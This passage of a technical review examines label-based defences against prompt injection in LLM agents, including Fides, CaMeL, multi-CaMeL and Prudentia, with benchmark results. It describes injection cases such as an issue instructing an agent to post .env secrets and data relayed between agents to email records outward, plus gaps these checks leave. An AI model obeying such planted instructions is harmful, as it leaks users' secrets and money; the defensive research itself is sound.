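| `auto_hide_untrusted` | On | Puts untrusted results in a variable store and shows the main model only a name |
| `quarantine_chat_client` | None | Sets the model that answers quarantined queries. Without one, the query tool returns placeholder text |
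| `default_integrity` | Untrusted | Labels results from tools that declare nothing |
| `block_on_violation` | On | Stops a call that breaks a policy |
| `approval_on_violation` | Off | Asks the user instead of stopping the call |
| `enable_policy_enforcement` | On | If off, the software still tracks labels but blocks nothing |

The `auto_hide_untrusted` setting matters most because it switches between the Dual LLM pattern and plain session taint. Microsoft's example is an agent that triages GitHub issues and can read files, write files and post comments. An attacker files an issue instructing it to read `.env`, a file that often holds passwords, and post the contents. With hiding off, the model reads the issue and may obey, but the software blocks the comment because reading the file has marked the context as private. With hiding on, the main model never reads the instruction, so it has no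 reason to open the file.

Hiding requires a second model call whenever the agent needs to know what an issue contains, and the agent then works from a summary or another extract. Hiding saves tokens in the main model if the issue is long, and the developer can use a cheaper model for the quarantined call. The main model can also request a hidden text in full, which Microsoft describes as explicitly revealing the data and tainting the agent's context.

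The option hides only untrusted results. A trusted, private file still enters the main context, and the software will then block public comments. Label creep remains a problem unless the developer explicitly drops the content. Microsoft is considering labels that cover single messages, or that decay when the software compacts a long conversation.

Microsoft's two accounts of the module disagree on points that affect security. According to the May announcement, an unlabelled tool is trusted and public by default, but according to the documentation it is untrusted and public. Under the announcement's default, forgetting to label a tool would let hostile text straight into the main context, as happened with Ruby's web queries. The announcement also describes a tool that refuses untrusted arguments, whereas the documentation describes a test of the context label. If the software tests only the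 context, untrusted text from a variable could end up in a file that the agent writes. A developer can settle the default by setting `default_integrity`, but should test the argument check before relying on it.

### One bit from the mailbox

The main model sometimes has to learn something from the hidden text before it can choose its next step. Costa and colleagues use the example of a user who asks the agent to read her three newest emails, check whether any of them requests a meeting and, if so, create the calendar event. With simplified names, the calls are:

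```
1. read_emails(number=3)                         -> emails_1
2. query_llm("Is there a meeting request?",
             input=emails_1, output=yes/no)      -> answer_1
3. inspect(answer_1)                             main model reads "yes"
4. query_llm("Extract the event details",
             input=emails_1, output=event form)  -> details_1
5. set_event(details_1)
```

The main model's context includes only the fact that a request exists. A quarantined model call copies the date, time and participants into a form, and the software passes the form to the calendar tool without adding it to the main model's context.

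The strict rule would still block `set_event`, because the main context now contains an answer that depends on untrusted emails. Costa and colleagues argue that a single yes or no is unlikely to carry an injection, so a policy may accept it. To support such a policy, they add an output type to each label and order the types by how much information they can carry:

```
yes/no   ⊑   one of a fixed list   ⊑   free text

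(untrusted, yes/no)  join  (untrusted, fixed list)  =  (untrusted, fixed list)
```

The software enforces the type through *constrained decoding*, which lets the quarantined model produce only tokens that fit the required form. A yes/no query can't return a sentence, however persuasive the email is. The user's own request needs the lowest type even though it is free text, because joining it with an untrusted yes would otherwise give "untrusted free text", and the policy would block the call.

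An answer with *n* possible values carries at most log₂ *n* bits:

| What the main model reads | Possible values | Most it can carry |
|---|---|---|
| One yes/no answer | 2 | 1 bit |
| One choice among eight | 8 | 3 bits |
| Ten yes/no answers | 2¹⁰ = 1,024 | 10 bits |
| 100 characters of plain English text | 95¹⁰⁰ | About 657 bits |

Ten yes/no answers can carry more information than one choice among eight, but the type order ranks them lower. Joining ten yes/no labels gives another yes/no label, so a policy that accepts this type accepts any number of such answers. A designer who wants to limit the total information has to count the bits separately.

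Ten bits can't encode even two typed characters, so an attacker can't send an instruction this way. But the harm depends on what the agent does with each answer. In the meeting task, a false yes leads to an unwanted calendar entry. If the question were whether an invoice is genuine, and the agent paid after a yes, an attacker could steal the money with one bit.

An attacker's email can supply every field of the event form, so the form carries much more than one bit. The policy has to allow untrusted arguments in `set_event` as well as an untrusted decision to call it. If the calendar tool emails invitations, the attacker can choose who receives one in the user's name, so limiting participants to her existing contacts would be sensible.

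Nobody has shown how many tasks the one-bit policy recovers. Costa and colleagues left constrained decoding out of their AgentDojo tests because most of the tasks didn't need it. Microsoft names constrained decoding as a possible next step for its products.

### What a subagent can hand back

A *subagent* is a separate agent that the main agent starts to do part of a job. It has its own context and, unlike a quarantined model, can have tools and work for many turns. Microsoft's module doesn't offer quarantined subagents yet, since its quarantined model answers one query and stops.

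A subagent's fresh context is clean only if the task it receives is clean. The same join rule covers the task going down and the result coming back:

```
at the start:        subagent_label = label of the parent's task message
after each read:     subagent_label = join(subagent_label, label of the data)
at the end:          label of the result = subagent_label
if the parent reads
the result:          parent_label = join(parent_label, label of the result)
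```

If a subagent reads ten web pages and returns a paragraph about them, the whole paragraph is untrusted. The parent hasn't seen any of the pages, but an instruction from one of them may have survived in the summary. Many developers use subagents to keep long documents out of the main context. A free-text summary serves that purpose, but it doesn't protect the integrity of the main context.

Suppose the Pacman developer wants an agent to read the open issues and then fix the most urgent bug. She could restart the session after it reads them, or have a subagent read the issues and report back.

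| Arrangement | What the main agent gets | Main agent's label | What is lost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Restart the session | Only what the user types | Trusted | Everything learned before the restart, including trusted work |
| Subagent with a fixed output form | An issue number and one of eight bug types | Untrusted, but with few bits | Any detail the form has no field for |
| Subagent with free text | A description of the bug | Untrusted | Consequential actions without approval |

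Meta advises restarting the session for jobs that need all three of its risky properties. This works if no untrusted text carries over into the new session. If the developer pastes the old session's summary into her new request, the software will label the stranger's text as hers. Willison's pattern has the same weakness, since it treats whatever the user types as trusted.

The fixed form suits sorting and routing. The main agent could open the right source file after learning that issue 12 concerns ghost movement, but it wouldn't know what the player saw. Free text would give it that detail but put it under the same limits as an agent under session taint. Those limits matter little when the main agent only has to report back to the user, because no consequential action follows. The main agent can also pass the text on without reading it, as Willison's controller does.

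Requiring a subagent to return its results in a fixed form protects only the parent agent. A hijacked subagent can still misuse its own tools, so the policy check has to run inside each subagent's context too.

### Taint that crosses between agents

In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) tested a system in which every agent has strong protection but the messages between agents have none. A main agent, the *orchestrator*, calls the other agents as if they were tools. Every agent runs CaMeL, a Google DeepMind design in which a privileged model writes its whole program before any data arrives.

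In one demonstration, a user asks for a summary of job applicants to be sent to Julie on Slack. An attacker has planted an instruction in the applicant database to email the data to an outside address.

1. The orchestrator asks a database agent for the records. Neither agent's privileged model reads them.
2. A quarantined model summarises the records, and the orchestrator's program pastes the summary into a sentence that asks a notification agent to send it to Julie.
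3. The notification agent treats that sentence as its user's request. Its privileged model reads the planted instruction and writes a program that messages Julie and also emails the outside address.

The orchestrator and the database agent run the same programs with or without the attack. Peters-Gill and colleagues use the term *boundary laundering* for this failure, in which untrusted data becomes a trusted instruction when it passes from one agent to another. The same thing happens when a triage agent posts a comment under a trusted GitHub account.

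They also prove that in any tree of two or more agents where some tool returns untrusted data, some user request lets that data shape an agent's instructions. The proof assumes that an agent can use one tool's result in its next call. If the agent that holds the tool has a subagent, it can put the result in the subagent's task. If it has a parent, it can return the result, and the parent can put it in the next task it sends down. Many requests will never create such a path, and protecting each agent separately does stop some attacks. An attack that tries to make a database agent open a private database failed in all five trials.

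Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each call between agents into two parts. The request to message Julie would become:

```
notification_agent(
    message   = "Post the stored summary to the named person on Slack.",
    variables = {"person": "Julie", "summary": summary_1}
)
```

The receiving agent's privileged model reads only `message`, and its program fetches the variables at run time. The software rejects a call if the message depends on any tool's output. The variables keep their labels, so a policy could in principle be used to track the data through the whole system.

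Peters-Gill and colleagues measured the effect by adapting AgentDojo, a benchmark of agent tasks with planted injections in simulated workspace, travel, banking and Slack settings. They divided each setting's tools among two to four subagents under an orchestrator. They tried 949 combinations of task and attack for each model and arrangement, and ran the 97 harmless tasks separately. The table gives their results.

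| Model | Attacks succeeding, no CaMeL | Attacks succeeding, CaMeL in each agent | Harmless tasks done, no CaMeL | Harmless tasks done, CaMeL in each agent | Harmless tasks done, multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 86.6% | 73.2% | 66.0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 69.1% | 53.6% | 52.6% |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 78.4% | 38.1% | 24.7% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 76.3% | 42.3% | 26.8% |
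| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 27.8% | 13.4% | 7.2% |

On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent and none with multi-CaMeL. The 0.2% was nine successes in 4,745 attempts, all by boundary laundering. The attacks came from the benchmark and didn't adapt to the defence, so a determined attacker who knew how the agents were connected could probably succeed more often against CaMeL in each agent.

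With multi-CaMeL, GPT-5.5 and Fable 5 each lost about a quarter of the tasks they had completed without CaMeL, while the other three models lost roughly two thirds to three quarters. Peters-Gill and colleagues describe the further loss from using multi-CaMeL instead of CaMeL in each agent as generally modest. GPT-4.1 lost a third of the tasks it could still complete with CaMeL in each agent, but the change stopped five attacks. Fable 5's completion rates are low partly because it refused 52 of the 97 harmless tasks, possibly because the setting looked like a security test. It completed 91.1% of the other 45 without CaMeL and 84.4% with either form.

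The losses were smaller on AssetOpsBench, a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks with an orchestrator and four subagents. After removing 29 tasks that no agent could complete as written, Peters-Gill and colleagues found that CaMeL in each agent lowered completion by 21.6 percentage points on average, and multi-CaMeL lowered it by a further 3.2. Model strength doesn't fully explain the losses. GPT-5.5 and Fable 5 did almost equally well without protection, but with multi-CaMeL GPT-5.5 lost 8 points and Fable 5 lost more than 20.

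Most failures happened because the privileged model had fixed its plan before it saw any data. In others, a subagent that couldn't find records for the exact machine or dates in its task returned records for something similar, and the orchestrator's prewritten program continued with the wrong data. An orchestrator that had read the reply might have noticed the mismatch.

The benchmark can also count poor work as success. In one run that Peters-Gill and colleagues present as a completed task, the user asks for feedback on Dora's website. The orchestrator's program sends Dora a message praising the site's "clean design", but the privileged model wrote that praise before the page was fetched. Apart from the planted instruction, the page contained only an email address and one line about whose site it was. The program also invites whatever address the quarantined model finds there to the Slack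 workspace, so someone who can edit the page could choose who is invited unless a policy checks the address. The study's tests used no such policies.

The software that enforces the split builds on CaMeL's interpreter, which misses some implicit flows, so a variable can keep a trusted label even when an untrusted value determined its contents. A message built from that variable would pass the check. The design also assumes that agents form a tree and communicate only through calls and replies. If agents share a memory or message each other directly, there may be no single point at which the software can separate instructions from data.

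## Fides and labels on individual tool results

A quarantined reader keeps a whole text away from the main agent, but often only part of a tool result needs hiding. In an email, the mail server can verify the sender's address and the date, but the sender controls the subject and body. Fides (Flow Integrity Deterministic Enforcement System), which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft in 2025, labels each field separately and hides only those that would taint the agent's context. They tested it against session taint with the same tasks, model and labels, so the results are directly comparable.

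### How a field becomes a variable

Fides splits the software around the model into two parts. The *planner* keeps the conversation history, the history's label and a store of hidden values, and decides what the model gets to read. The *planning loop* calls the model, checks the policy and runs the tools. When an agent with a trusted context reads its user's mail, they work like this:

1. A wrapper around the mail tool attaches a label to each field of the result.
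2. The planner stores each field that would raise the context's label under a new name and puts only the name in the history. It leaves the other fields readable.
3. When the model uses a name in its next call, the planner restores the stored value and its label, and the loop checks the policy before running the tool.
4. The loop labels the tool's result, and anything the tool wrote, with the join of the labels on the call, its arguments and the data the tool may have read.

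If the sender and date are trusted, one email would look like this before and after step 2, with names shortened:

```
what the tool returns                   what the model reads

sender:  "marco@corp.example"  trusted    sender:  "marco@corp.example"
date:    "3 March"             trusted    date:    "3 March"
subject: "Quick question"      untrusted  subject: #emails_0.subject#
body:    "Hi, could you ..."   untrusted  body:    #emails_0.body#
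```

The real names also include the tool and call that produced the value and its position in a list, so the model can distinguish the third email's body from the first email's subject without reading either.

The function that does the hiding is short and works its way down through lists and records:

```
hide(value, label):
    if label is not at or below context_label:
        store (value, label) under a new name
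        return the name
    if value is a list or a record:
        return it with hide() applied to each part
    return value
```

The function compares each label with the current context, so the same email can be hidden at one moment and readable at another. Once the context is untrusted, more untrusted text can't raise the context's label, so the planner shows it in full. In Willison's Dual LLM pattern, the controller always withholds untrusted text from the privileged model. Under Fides, the model can open a variable with a tool called `inspect`, which taints the context, or ask a quarantined model about the hidden text.

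### Sending three emails to a colleague

Suppose the user asks the agent to read her top three emails and send them to Dana on Slack. The *basic planner* puts every tool result in the context and keeps one label for the whole context, which is session taint. The *variable planner* stores the emails in a named variable. For simplicity, the table treats the emails as one untrusted value.

| Step | Basic planner | Variable planner |
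|---|---|---|
| `read_emails(number=3)` | The text enters the context, which becomes untrusted | The planner stores the text as `emails_1`, and the context stays trusted |
| The model's next call | `send_message(to="Dana", message=` the full text of the emails`)` | `send_message(to="Dana", message=emails_1)` |
| Labels | Call, recipient and message are all untrusted | Call and recipient are trusted, message is untrusted |
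| Did the model choose the call from trusted inputs alone? | No, so the software blocks it | Yes, so the message goes out |

Dana would get the same message from either agent, but only the variable planner lets the software be sure that no email changed the recipient.

The strict integrity rule would still block the message because its text is untrusted, so in their experiment Costa and colleagues checked only the call's own label. This check suits a request to forward emails, since the user wants Dana to have them whatever they contain.

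A result can still reveal information when its fields are hidden. In one of Costa and colleagues' traces, a user asks the agent to find the Slack channel with the fewest messages and add Alice to it. The software hides the channel names and message text, but the model can still see how many messages are in each list. One list is empty, so the model adds Alice to that channel, using the channel's variable name. The call counts as trusted, although anyone who can post in those channels can change which one has the fewest messages. This is an implicit flow through the shape of the data. It does little harm here, but it could matter if the agent gave out access or money based on a count.

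### The AgentDojo comparison

Costa and colleagues ran both planners on AgentDojo's 97 user tasks, using GPT-4o and averaging over five runs. They first replaced the benchmark's tools with wrapped versions that return labels, and then gave 27 tools a policy:

- For 21 tools, including those that send money, delete email and book hotels, the call's label must be trusted.
- For five tools that write or send text, including email, Slack messages and new calendar events, passing either of two tests is enough. The call's label is trusted, or every recipient may read the text and it contains no untrusted link.
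- Adding people to a calendar event requires passing both tests.

The link test stops an agent from leaking data through a web address that a stranger supplied. The table gives the percentage of user tasks completed without an attack, including a repeat run with OpenAI's reasoning model o1. Both models are old now.

| Model | Planner | Policy checks | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
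| GPT-4o | Basic | Off | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| GPT-4o | Basic | On | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| GPT-4o | Fides | Off | 63.5 | 50.0 | 65.0 | 63.8 |
| GPT-4o | Fides | On | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |
| o1 | Basic | Off | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 |
| o1 | Basic | On | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 |
| o1 | Fides | Off | 77.5 | 75.0 | 78.8 | 79.0 |
| o1 | Fides | On | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 |

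With policy checks, Fides completed more tasks than the basic planner in every setting except travel. Costa and colleagues reported an average advantage of 8 percentage points with GPT-4o and 16 with o1. Their average weights the four settings equally, although workspace has 40 tasks and banking only 16. Weighting every task equally raises the advantage to about 11 points with GPT-4o and leaves it at about 16 with o1. Costa and colleagues later reported an advantage of 24% after further tuning the prompt.

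The two planners fail tasks for different reasons. The basic planner with GPT-4o averaged 84% without checks and 42% with them, so blocked calls caused the whole drop. Fides averaged 61% even with the checks off, because GPT-4o often confused the names of variables or failed to query the quarantined model when it should have. Turning the checks on lowered its average by another 11 points. With o1, Fides lost about 6 points to handling variables and about 17 to the checks.

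A better model therefore helped Fides much more than it helped the basic planner. In banking, the basic planner completed 37.5% of tasks with either model, because an untrusted label blocks payments however well the model reasons.

The results may overstate how well Fides performs, because Costa and colleagues tuned its instructions on the workspace tasks and then tested it on the same tasks. However, its lead over the basic planner was larger in Slack, where they had done no tuning, than in workspace.

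Models can also complete some of the benchmark's tasks by guessing. Costa and colleagues tested a simpler planner that hides untrusted results from the model and gives it no way to read or ask about them. They classified none of the travel tasks as solvable this way, but with GPT-4o the planner completed 43.0% of them without policy checks. In some cases the model recommended a highly rated hotel without having seen any ratings. With o1 the planner completed only 2.0%. Some of GPT-4o's successes under Fides were probably guesses too.

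### Travel and banking

The coarse rule did better on travel tasks because it rarely applied. Many of these tasks need only tools that may run in an untrusted context if every recipient of the text is allowed to read it, and no travel task broke that condition. The basic planner could therefore read all the reviews and answer freely, and its score was about the same with the checks on or off.

Fides had to solve the same tasks with untrusted text hidden in variables. Costa and colleagues classed 90% of the travel tasks as requiring the agent to ask a quarantined model about hidden text, which GPT-4o did unreliably. With o1, the gap between the two planners shrank from 32 points to 7. A designer could avoid the problem by keeping untrusted text readable in sessions where no strict policy is likely to apply, but the software would have to identify those sessions before the agent reads anything.

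In banking, many tasks fail because the user asks for something the policy forbids. Several tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, for example to schedule a payment or update the user's details. Like the request to complete the tasks in a to-do app, these require the main model to read untrusted text, and the policy then blocks the payment. A landlord's genuine notice of a rent increase and a forged one both arrive as untrusted text that asks for money. A label can't distinguish them, so someone has to approve the notice or the payment.

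Costa and colleagues sorted all 97 tasks by hand to estimate how well Fides could do with a perfect model. Its natural limit is the share of tasks that an agent can complete while the main model reads no untrusted text:

| | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Solvable without the main model reading untrusted text | 95.0% | 90.0% | 56.2% | 57.1% |
| Completed by Fides with o1 and policy checks | 64.5% | 68.0% | 56.2% | 54.3% |

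Costa and colleagues conclude that Fides approaches the performance of a human oracle as models improve. That holds for banking and Slack, but in workspace and travel Fides was still 22 to 30 points short. Even in banking, where it matched the oracle, Fides didn't complete exactly the tasks it was supposed to. One task asks the agent to change the user's password if it finds a suspicious transaction, which should require reading the transactions' descriptions. The model saw only dates and amounts, decided that a large amount looked suspicious, and changed the password. The policy allowed the change because the context was still trusted.

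### Attacks with and without policy checks

To measure security, Costa and colleagues paired each user task with every injection task in the same setting. The four settings have 36 injection tasks in total. They used a strong version of the benchmark's standard attack, in which the attacker knows the agent's tools and plants instructions for a particular sequence of calls. They also tested *Tool Filter*, a defence that prompts the model at the start of each task to discard the tools it won't need. The table gives the number of successful attacks after they reviewed the benchmark's scoring by hand.

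| Planner | Policy checks off | Policy checks on |
|---|---|---|
| Basic | 152 | 0 |
| Tool Filter | 20 | Not tested |
| Variables only, with no way to read them | 0 | 0 |
| Fides | 21 | 0 |

Without policy checks, Fides did no better than Tool Filter. The model could still open an untrusted variable, read the planted instruction and obey it. Hiding untrusted text reduces the model's exposure to it, but only the policy check guarantees that the model makes no forbidden call after reading it.

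The zeros also depend on what counts as an attack. With the checks on, the benchmark still recorded 20 successful attacks against the basic planner (though the figures for the four settings add up to 18) and three against Fides. Costa and colleagues removed them for three reasons. Some were calls that the policy had blocked but the benchmark still counted, such as an invitation to the Slack workspace. Others were actions the policy permitted, such as creating a calendar event without participants or sending a link-free Slack message to people allowed to read it. The rest only changed the agent's text, for instance by making it recommend a particular place to visit.

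The first reason corrects an error. The other two count an attack as successful only if it breaks the policy, which policy checks prevent almost by construction. A user who finds a stranger's event in her calendar, or books a hotel because of a planted recommendation, may still consider the attack successful. Costa and colleagues point out that Fides still labels such text as untrusted, so an application could warn the user or withhold the text.

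Checking only the call's label also leaves a gap that the benchmark's attack did not test. Suppose the user asks the agent to pay a bill stored as a file. The agent keeps the file hidden, has a quarantined model extract the account number and the amount, and passes both to `send_money` as variables. The call is trusted, so the policy allows the payment. Someone who had changed the account number in the file would receive the money without giving the agent any instruction. Requiring a trusted recipient would prevent this, but the agent could then pay only people whose details came from a trusted source.

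The checks caused little extra disruption during attacks. Under attack and with checks on, Fides completed 64.0% of workspace tasks, 37.9% of travel tasks, 56.9% of banking tasks and 41.9% of Slack tasks. The basic planner completed 43.4%, 66.4%, 37.5% and 9.5%, respectively. When the policy blocked a call, the software notified the model, which could continue with the rest of the task.

### Labels taken from the benchmark's attacks

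AgentDojo doesn't come with labels, so Costa and colleagues chose their own. They marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's injection tasks targets it, and treated the rest as trusted. For example, if any injection sits in the body of an email, every email body is untrusted. They used this method to get a clear baseline, and considered alternatives such as trusting sender addresses that the mail server has authenticated.

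No planted instruction in the test could therefore be in a trusted field, and under-tainting, the error that lets attacks through, could not happen when data entered the system. So the zeros in the table show that the policy checks work when the labels are right. They are not evidence of how often a company would label its own data correctly.

The labels also affect how many tasks the agents complete. Transaction amounts counted as trusted because no injection task uses them, but the sender of a payment chooses its amount. In the password task, a stranger could have prompted the change by transferring an unusually large sum. A cautious bank would mark incoming amounts as untrusted, which would leave an agent under Fides with less data it could read.

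In other places the labels were stricter than necessary. A user asked for a password reset link from her mailbox, and the agent failed because every email body had the same label, so it couldn't distinguish a trusted sender's link from any other. Labels based on the sender might have prevented this failure.

Both planners used the same labels, so the comparison between them is more reliable than the individual percentages. More realistic labels could change the gap in either direction. If a tool result already contains an untrusted field, marking a second one untrusted makes no difference to the basic planner, but Fides has to hide a field it could otherwise have read. If a result had no untrusted fields, marking one untrusted taints the basic planner's whole context, while Fides only has to hide that field.

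The experiment mainly tested the integrity side of the design. The software created variables only for untrusted fields, never for private ones, and relied on the policy alone to prevent leaks. The wrappers also labelled data only one level deep, so a record inside another record had a single label.

### Explicit secrecy

For confidentiality, Costa and colleagues claim that the planning loop can enforce *explicit secrecy*, a property that earlier researchers defined for taint tracking in ordinary programs. It concerns an attacker who can see all public data and watch it change. The tools' data is a store of values, each either public or private. Every run of the agent makes a particular series of tool calls, and together these calls have some effect *g* on the store. Explicit secrecy requires that:

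```
for all stores d1 and d2:
    if d1 and d2 have the same public values,
    then g(d1) and g(d2) have the same public values
```

Under explicit secrecy, changing only the private data must not change what the same calls make public. For example, a tool call that copies a private file containing Dana's salary into a public channel violates this condition, because a different salary would put different text in the channel.

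Suppose the agent reads the file and then calls `close_ticket()` on a public support ticket only if Dana's salary is above 50,000. The definition of explicit secrecy keeps the series of calls fixed and varies only the data. Reading the file and closing the ticket has the same public effect whatever the file contains, so the run satisfies the definition. Anyone who knows the condition and watches the ticket still learns whether Dana earns more than 50,000, an implicit flow that the design deliberately does not block.

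Read literally, the May 2025 definition is also weaker than the policy check, because it treats the agent's conversation and stored variables as part of the program rather than as data. If the agent reads the salary in one call and types the figure into a message in the next, the second call posts a fixed string, which satisfies the definition. Unless the policy accepts any message from a trusted context, the confidentiality check would stop that message, because its text is labeled private and some of the channel's members aren't allowed to read it.

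The paper proves only the lemma that *g* matches what a run did to the store. It states without proof that the loop enforces explicit secrecy. The formal model assumes that the language model always gives the same reply to the same input, and it leaves out leaks through timing or the size of network traffic. Someone also has to list everything each tool might read or write, because the loop uses those lists to label results.

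Explicit secrecy concerns only leaks. Fides protects integrity more fully, because the label on a tool call also reflects text that influenced only the decision to make the call.

### Whether the model enforces the policy

In their September 2026 paper on FlowSeal, Shim and colleagues claim that all of Fides's policy enforcement is "performed by the LLM backend". If so, an attacker who confused the model could also disable the protection. They conclude that Fides is vulnerable to their attacks, including one in which Emily uses a shared page to learn Mark's diagnosis.

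The claim about enforcement is wrong. In simplified form, the part of Fides's planning loop that handles tool calls reads:

```
when the planner returns a tool call:
    if policy(call and its labels) is false:  abort
    otherwise:                                run the tool
```

The `policy` function compares labels in ordinary code, so the model does not decide the result. The version that Microsoft (2026) released for developers does the same in *middleware*, a layer of software between the agent and its tools. Consistent with this, the same planner and model allowed 21 attacks with the checks off and none with them on.

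The model decides which variables to open and when to query the quarantined model. Opening a variable it doesn't need raises the context's label and may prevent it from finishing the task. The loop records the higher label, so the mistake makes the policy stricter.

Shim and colleagues did not run Fides because, they explain, it serves a different purpose and, as a notebook, doesn't fit their test system. Ecosyste.ms' *fides*, an index entry for Microsoft's code, does describe a tutorial notebook, tested with GPT-4o and GPT-4.1. So it is unknown whether Shim and colleagues' attacks would work against Fides. That depends mostly on how Emily's messages reach the agent.

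If the agent uses a tool to read her request from an email or a shared page, the tool can label the request untrusted. The agent then can't write Mark's diagnosis on her page, because the context is untrusted and she isn't a permitted reader. A policy that allows deletions only when the context is trusted would also stop the agent from removing the false entries.

The result would be different if Emily talked to the agent directly and the developer passed her words to the model as user messages. Fides treats user messages as trusted unless someone labels them otherwise, and the experiment's policy for sending text accepts any message from a trusted context. Emily could then get the diagnosis by asking for it, even if every check worked as designed.

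## Prudentia and the cost of labels in human approvals

In Costa and colleagues' test, the software refused any call that broke the policy, and the agent often failed the task as a result. Products usually ask the user instead. GitHub Copilot Chat in Visual Studio Code, for example, runs read-only tools automatically but asks before using others. Kolluri and colleagues, most of whom also worked on Fides, therefore argue that counting failed tasks is the wrong way to measure the burden of labels. Earlier studies compared a labelled agent that could never ask for help with an unprotected agent whose calls all went through. If people would otherwise have to approve every consequential action, the benefit of labels is the number of approvals they make unnecessary.

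### Two ways to count approvals

Kolluri and colleagues record every tool call an agent makes on a task, a list they call a trace, and count the calls that break the policy. Each of these would need a person's approval. They define two measures from that count:

```
v(trace)       =  number of calls in the trace that break the policy

approval load  =  sum of v(trace) over the tasks the agent completed

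TCR@k          =  completed tasks with v(trace) <= k
                  ----------------------------------
                              all tasks
```

TCR stands for task completion rate. TCR@0 is the share of tasks the agent completes without asking anyone, and TCR@∞ is the share it completes when it can ask without limit.

Suppose an agent attempts five tasks:

| Task | Outcome | Calls needing approval |
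|---|---|---|
| 1 | Completed | 0 |
| 2 | Completed | 0 |
| 3 | Completed | 1 |
| 4 | Completed | 3 |
| 5 | Failed | 6 |

The approval load is 0 + 0 + 1 + 3 = 4. The six calls on the failed task don't count toward it. TCR@0 is 40%, TCR@1 is 60%, and TCR@3 is 80%, which is the highest TCR for any number of approvals. If the agent had also failed task 4, its load would have dropped from 4 to 1, even though it would have completed one task fewer.

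### Approvals on AgentDojo

Kolluri and colleagues compared four agents on AgentDojo's user tasks without attacks, using Costa and colleagues' policies and averaging over five runs. One agent asks before every consequential action. Another uses session taint and asks only when a call fails the policy check. Fides and Prudentia, which they built on Fides's code, also ask only about calls that fail. These are the results with OpenAI's reasoning model o3-mini:

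| Agent | Approval load | Completed with no approvals | With at most one | With any number |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Asks every time | 48.2 | 24.3% | 54.4% | 62.5% |
| Session taint | 32.4 | 35.5% | 58.8% | 62.5% |
| Fides | 18.8 | 50.1% | 60.8% | 64.3% |
| Prudentia | 16.4 | 59.1% | 66.1% | 69.8% |

Session taint removed a third of the approvals without losing any tasks, because it doesn't change what the model reads. Fides removed more than 40% of the remaining approvals.

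The approval loads are totals for the whole benchmark, so even the agent that asks every time needed fewer than one approval per completed task on average. One approval is often enough for a task. Fides completed 14.6 percentage points more tasks than session taint when no approvals were allowed, but only 2 points more when each task could have at most one. On this benchmark, value labels therefore add little for a user who is at the keyboard and willing to answer one question per task, but they help a lot when an agent runs overnight with nobody to approve its actions.

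The gaps in the paper's text are smaller. Without approvals, session taint is 9.7 points ahead of asking every time, and Fides is 10.7 points ahead of session taint. These figures are for o4-mini, although the neighbouring paragraph discusses o3-mini's loads. For o3-mini, the appendix gives 11.2 and 14.6 points. The claim that session taint and Fides cut approvals by a factor of 1.5 to 2.6 fits o3-mini but not o4-mini, where the factors are about 1.4 and 1.3.

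The appendix also has results for three other models:

| Model | Agent | Approval load | Completed with no approvals | With at most one | With any number |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | Asks every time | 59.4 | 28.0% | 63.1% | 72.2% |
| GPT-4o | Session taint | 39.4 | 38.4% | 66.6% | 72.2% |
| GPT-4o | Fides | 7.8 | 50.3% | 54.6% | 56.3% |
| GPT-4o | Prudentia | 23.8 | 42.5% | 58.4% | 61.4% |
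| o4-mini | Asks every time | 48.6 | 32.8% | 62.9% | 70.1% |
| o4-mini | Session taint | 34.6 | 42.5% | 66.0% | 70.1% |
| o4-mini | Fides | 36.8 | 53.2% | 68.5% | 75.7% |
| o4-mini | Prudentia | 19.2 | 59.4% | 70.3% | 73.2% |
| GPT-5 | Asks every time | 52.0 | 35.1% | 63.2% | 72.3% |
| GPT-5 | Session taint | 40.4 | 43.4% | 66.2% | 72.3% |
| GPT-5 | Fides | 41.3 | 57.1% | 72.7% | 78.9% |
| GPT-5 | Prudentia | 7.3 | 72.7% | 79.5% | 80.0% |

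With o4-mini and GPT-5, Fides needed about as many approvals as session taint, though it completed more tasks. Hiding text in variables saves no further approvals once the model has opened one, and the Fides model, which doesn't know the policies, can open variables it doesn't need.

Prudentia made the biggest difference with GPT-5, where it completed as many tasks without any approvals as session taint did with unlimited approvals. Its approval load was less than a fifth of Fides's. The paper's headline figures, up to 1.9 times fewer approvals than Fides and up to 9 points more tasks completed without approvals, exclude this result, so they understate the gain with the strongest model.

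With GPT-4o, Prudentia needed three times as many approvals as Fides and completed fewer tasks without them, so the claim that it reduces the approval load compared with every other agent doesn't hold for that model. GPT-4o is the only one of the four models that isn't a reasoning model, and Kolluri and colleagues observe that reasoning models handle hidden variables and policies better.

### A browser agent

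The WASP benchmark tests agents that control a web browser on simulated copies of the code-hosting site GitLab and the forum Reddit. The user always asks the agent to post a comment or upvote a post, and an attacker has planted instructions in a forum post or a GitLab issue. Kolluri and colleagues marked everything the sites' users wrote as untrusted and hid it in variables, but trusted the sites' own buttons and text boxes. They classed seven of the agent's 12 tools as consequential, including those for clicking, typing and opening a web address.

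The agent that asks every time needed between 2.9 and 3.7 approvals per task on GitLab, depending on the model, and between 1.0 and 1.7 on Reddit. Kolluri and colleagues give no figures for session taint but report that it performed similarly to asking every time. Under session taint, the first page brings strangers' text into the context, and after that every click needs approval.

Prudentia needed no approvals on WASP. It also completed at least as many tasks in all eight combinations of model and site, because the planted text couldn't distract it. Fides did about as well, so the reduction in approvals comes from hiding text, which both agents do.

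In 14.6% to 61.1% of cases, attacks diverted the agent that asks for approval every time. They never diverted Prudentia. The first agent's rates make sense only if the user approves the harmful clicks. For AgentDojo, however, Kolluri and colleagues assumed that the user would refuse every harmful action.

WASP is about as favourable to value labels as a benchmark can be, since all its tasks are data independent.

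### What Prudentia adds

Prudentia's policy check is the same as Fides's. Kolluri and colleagues changed the model's instructions and tools so that it could plan around the check:

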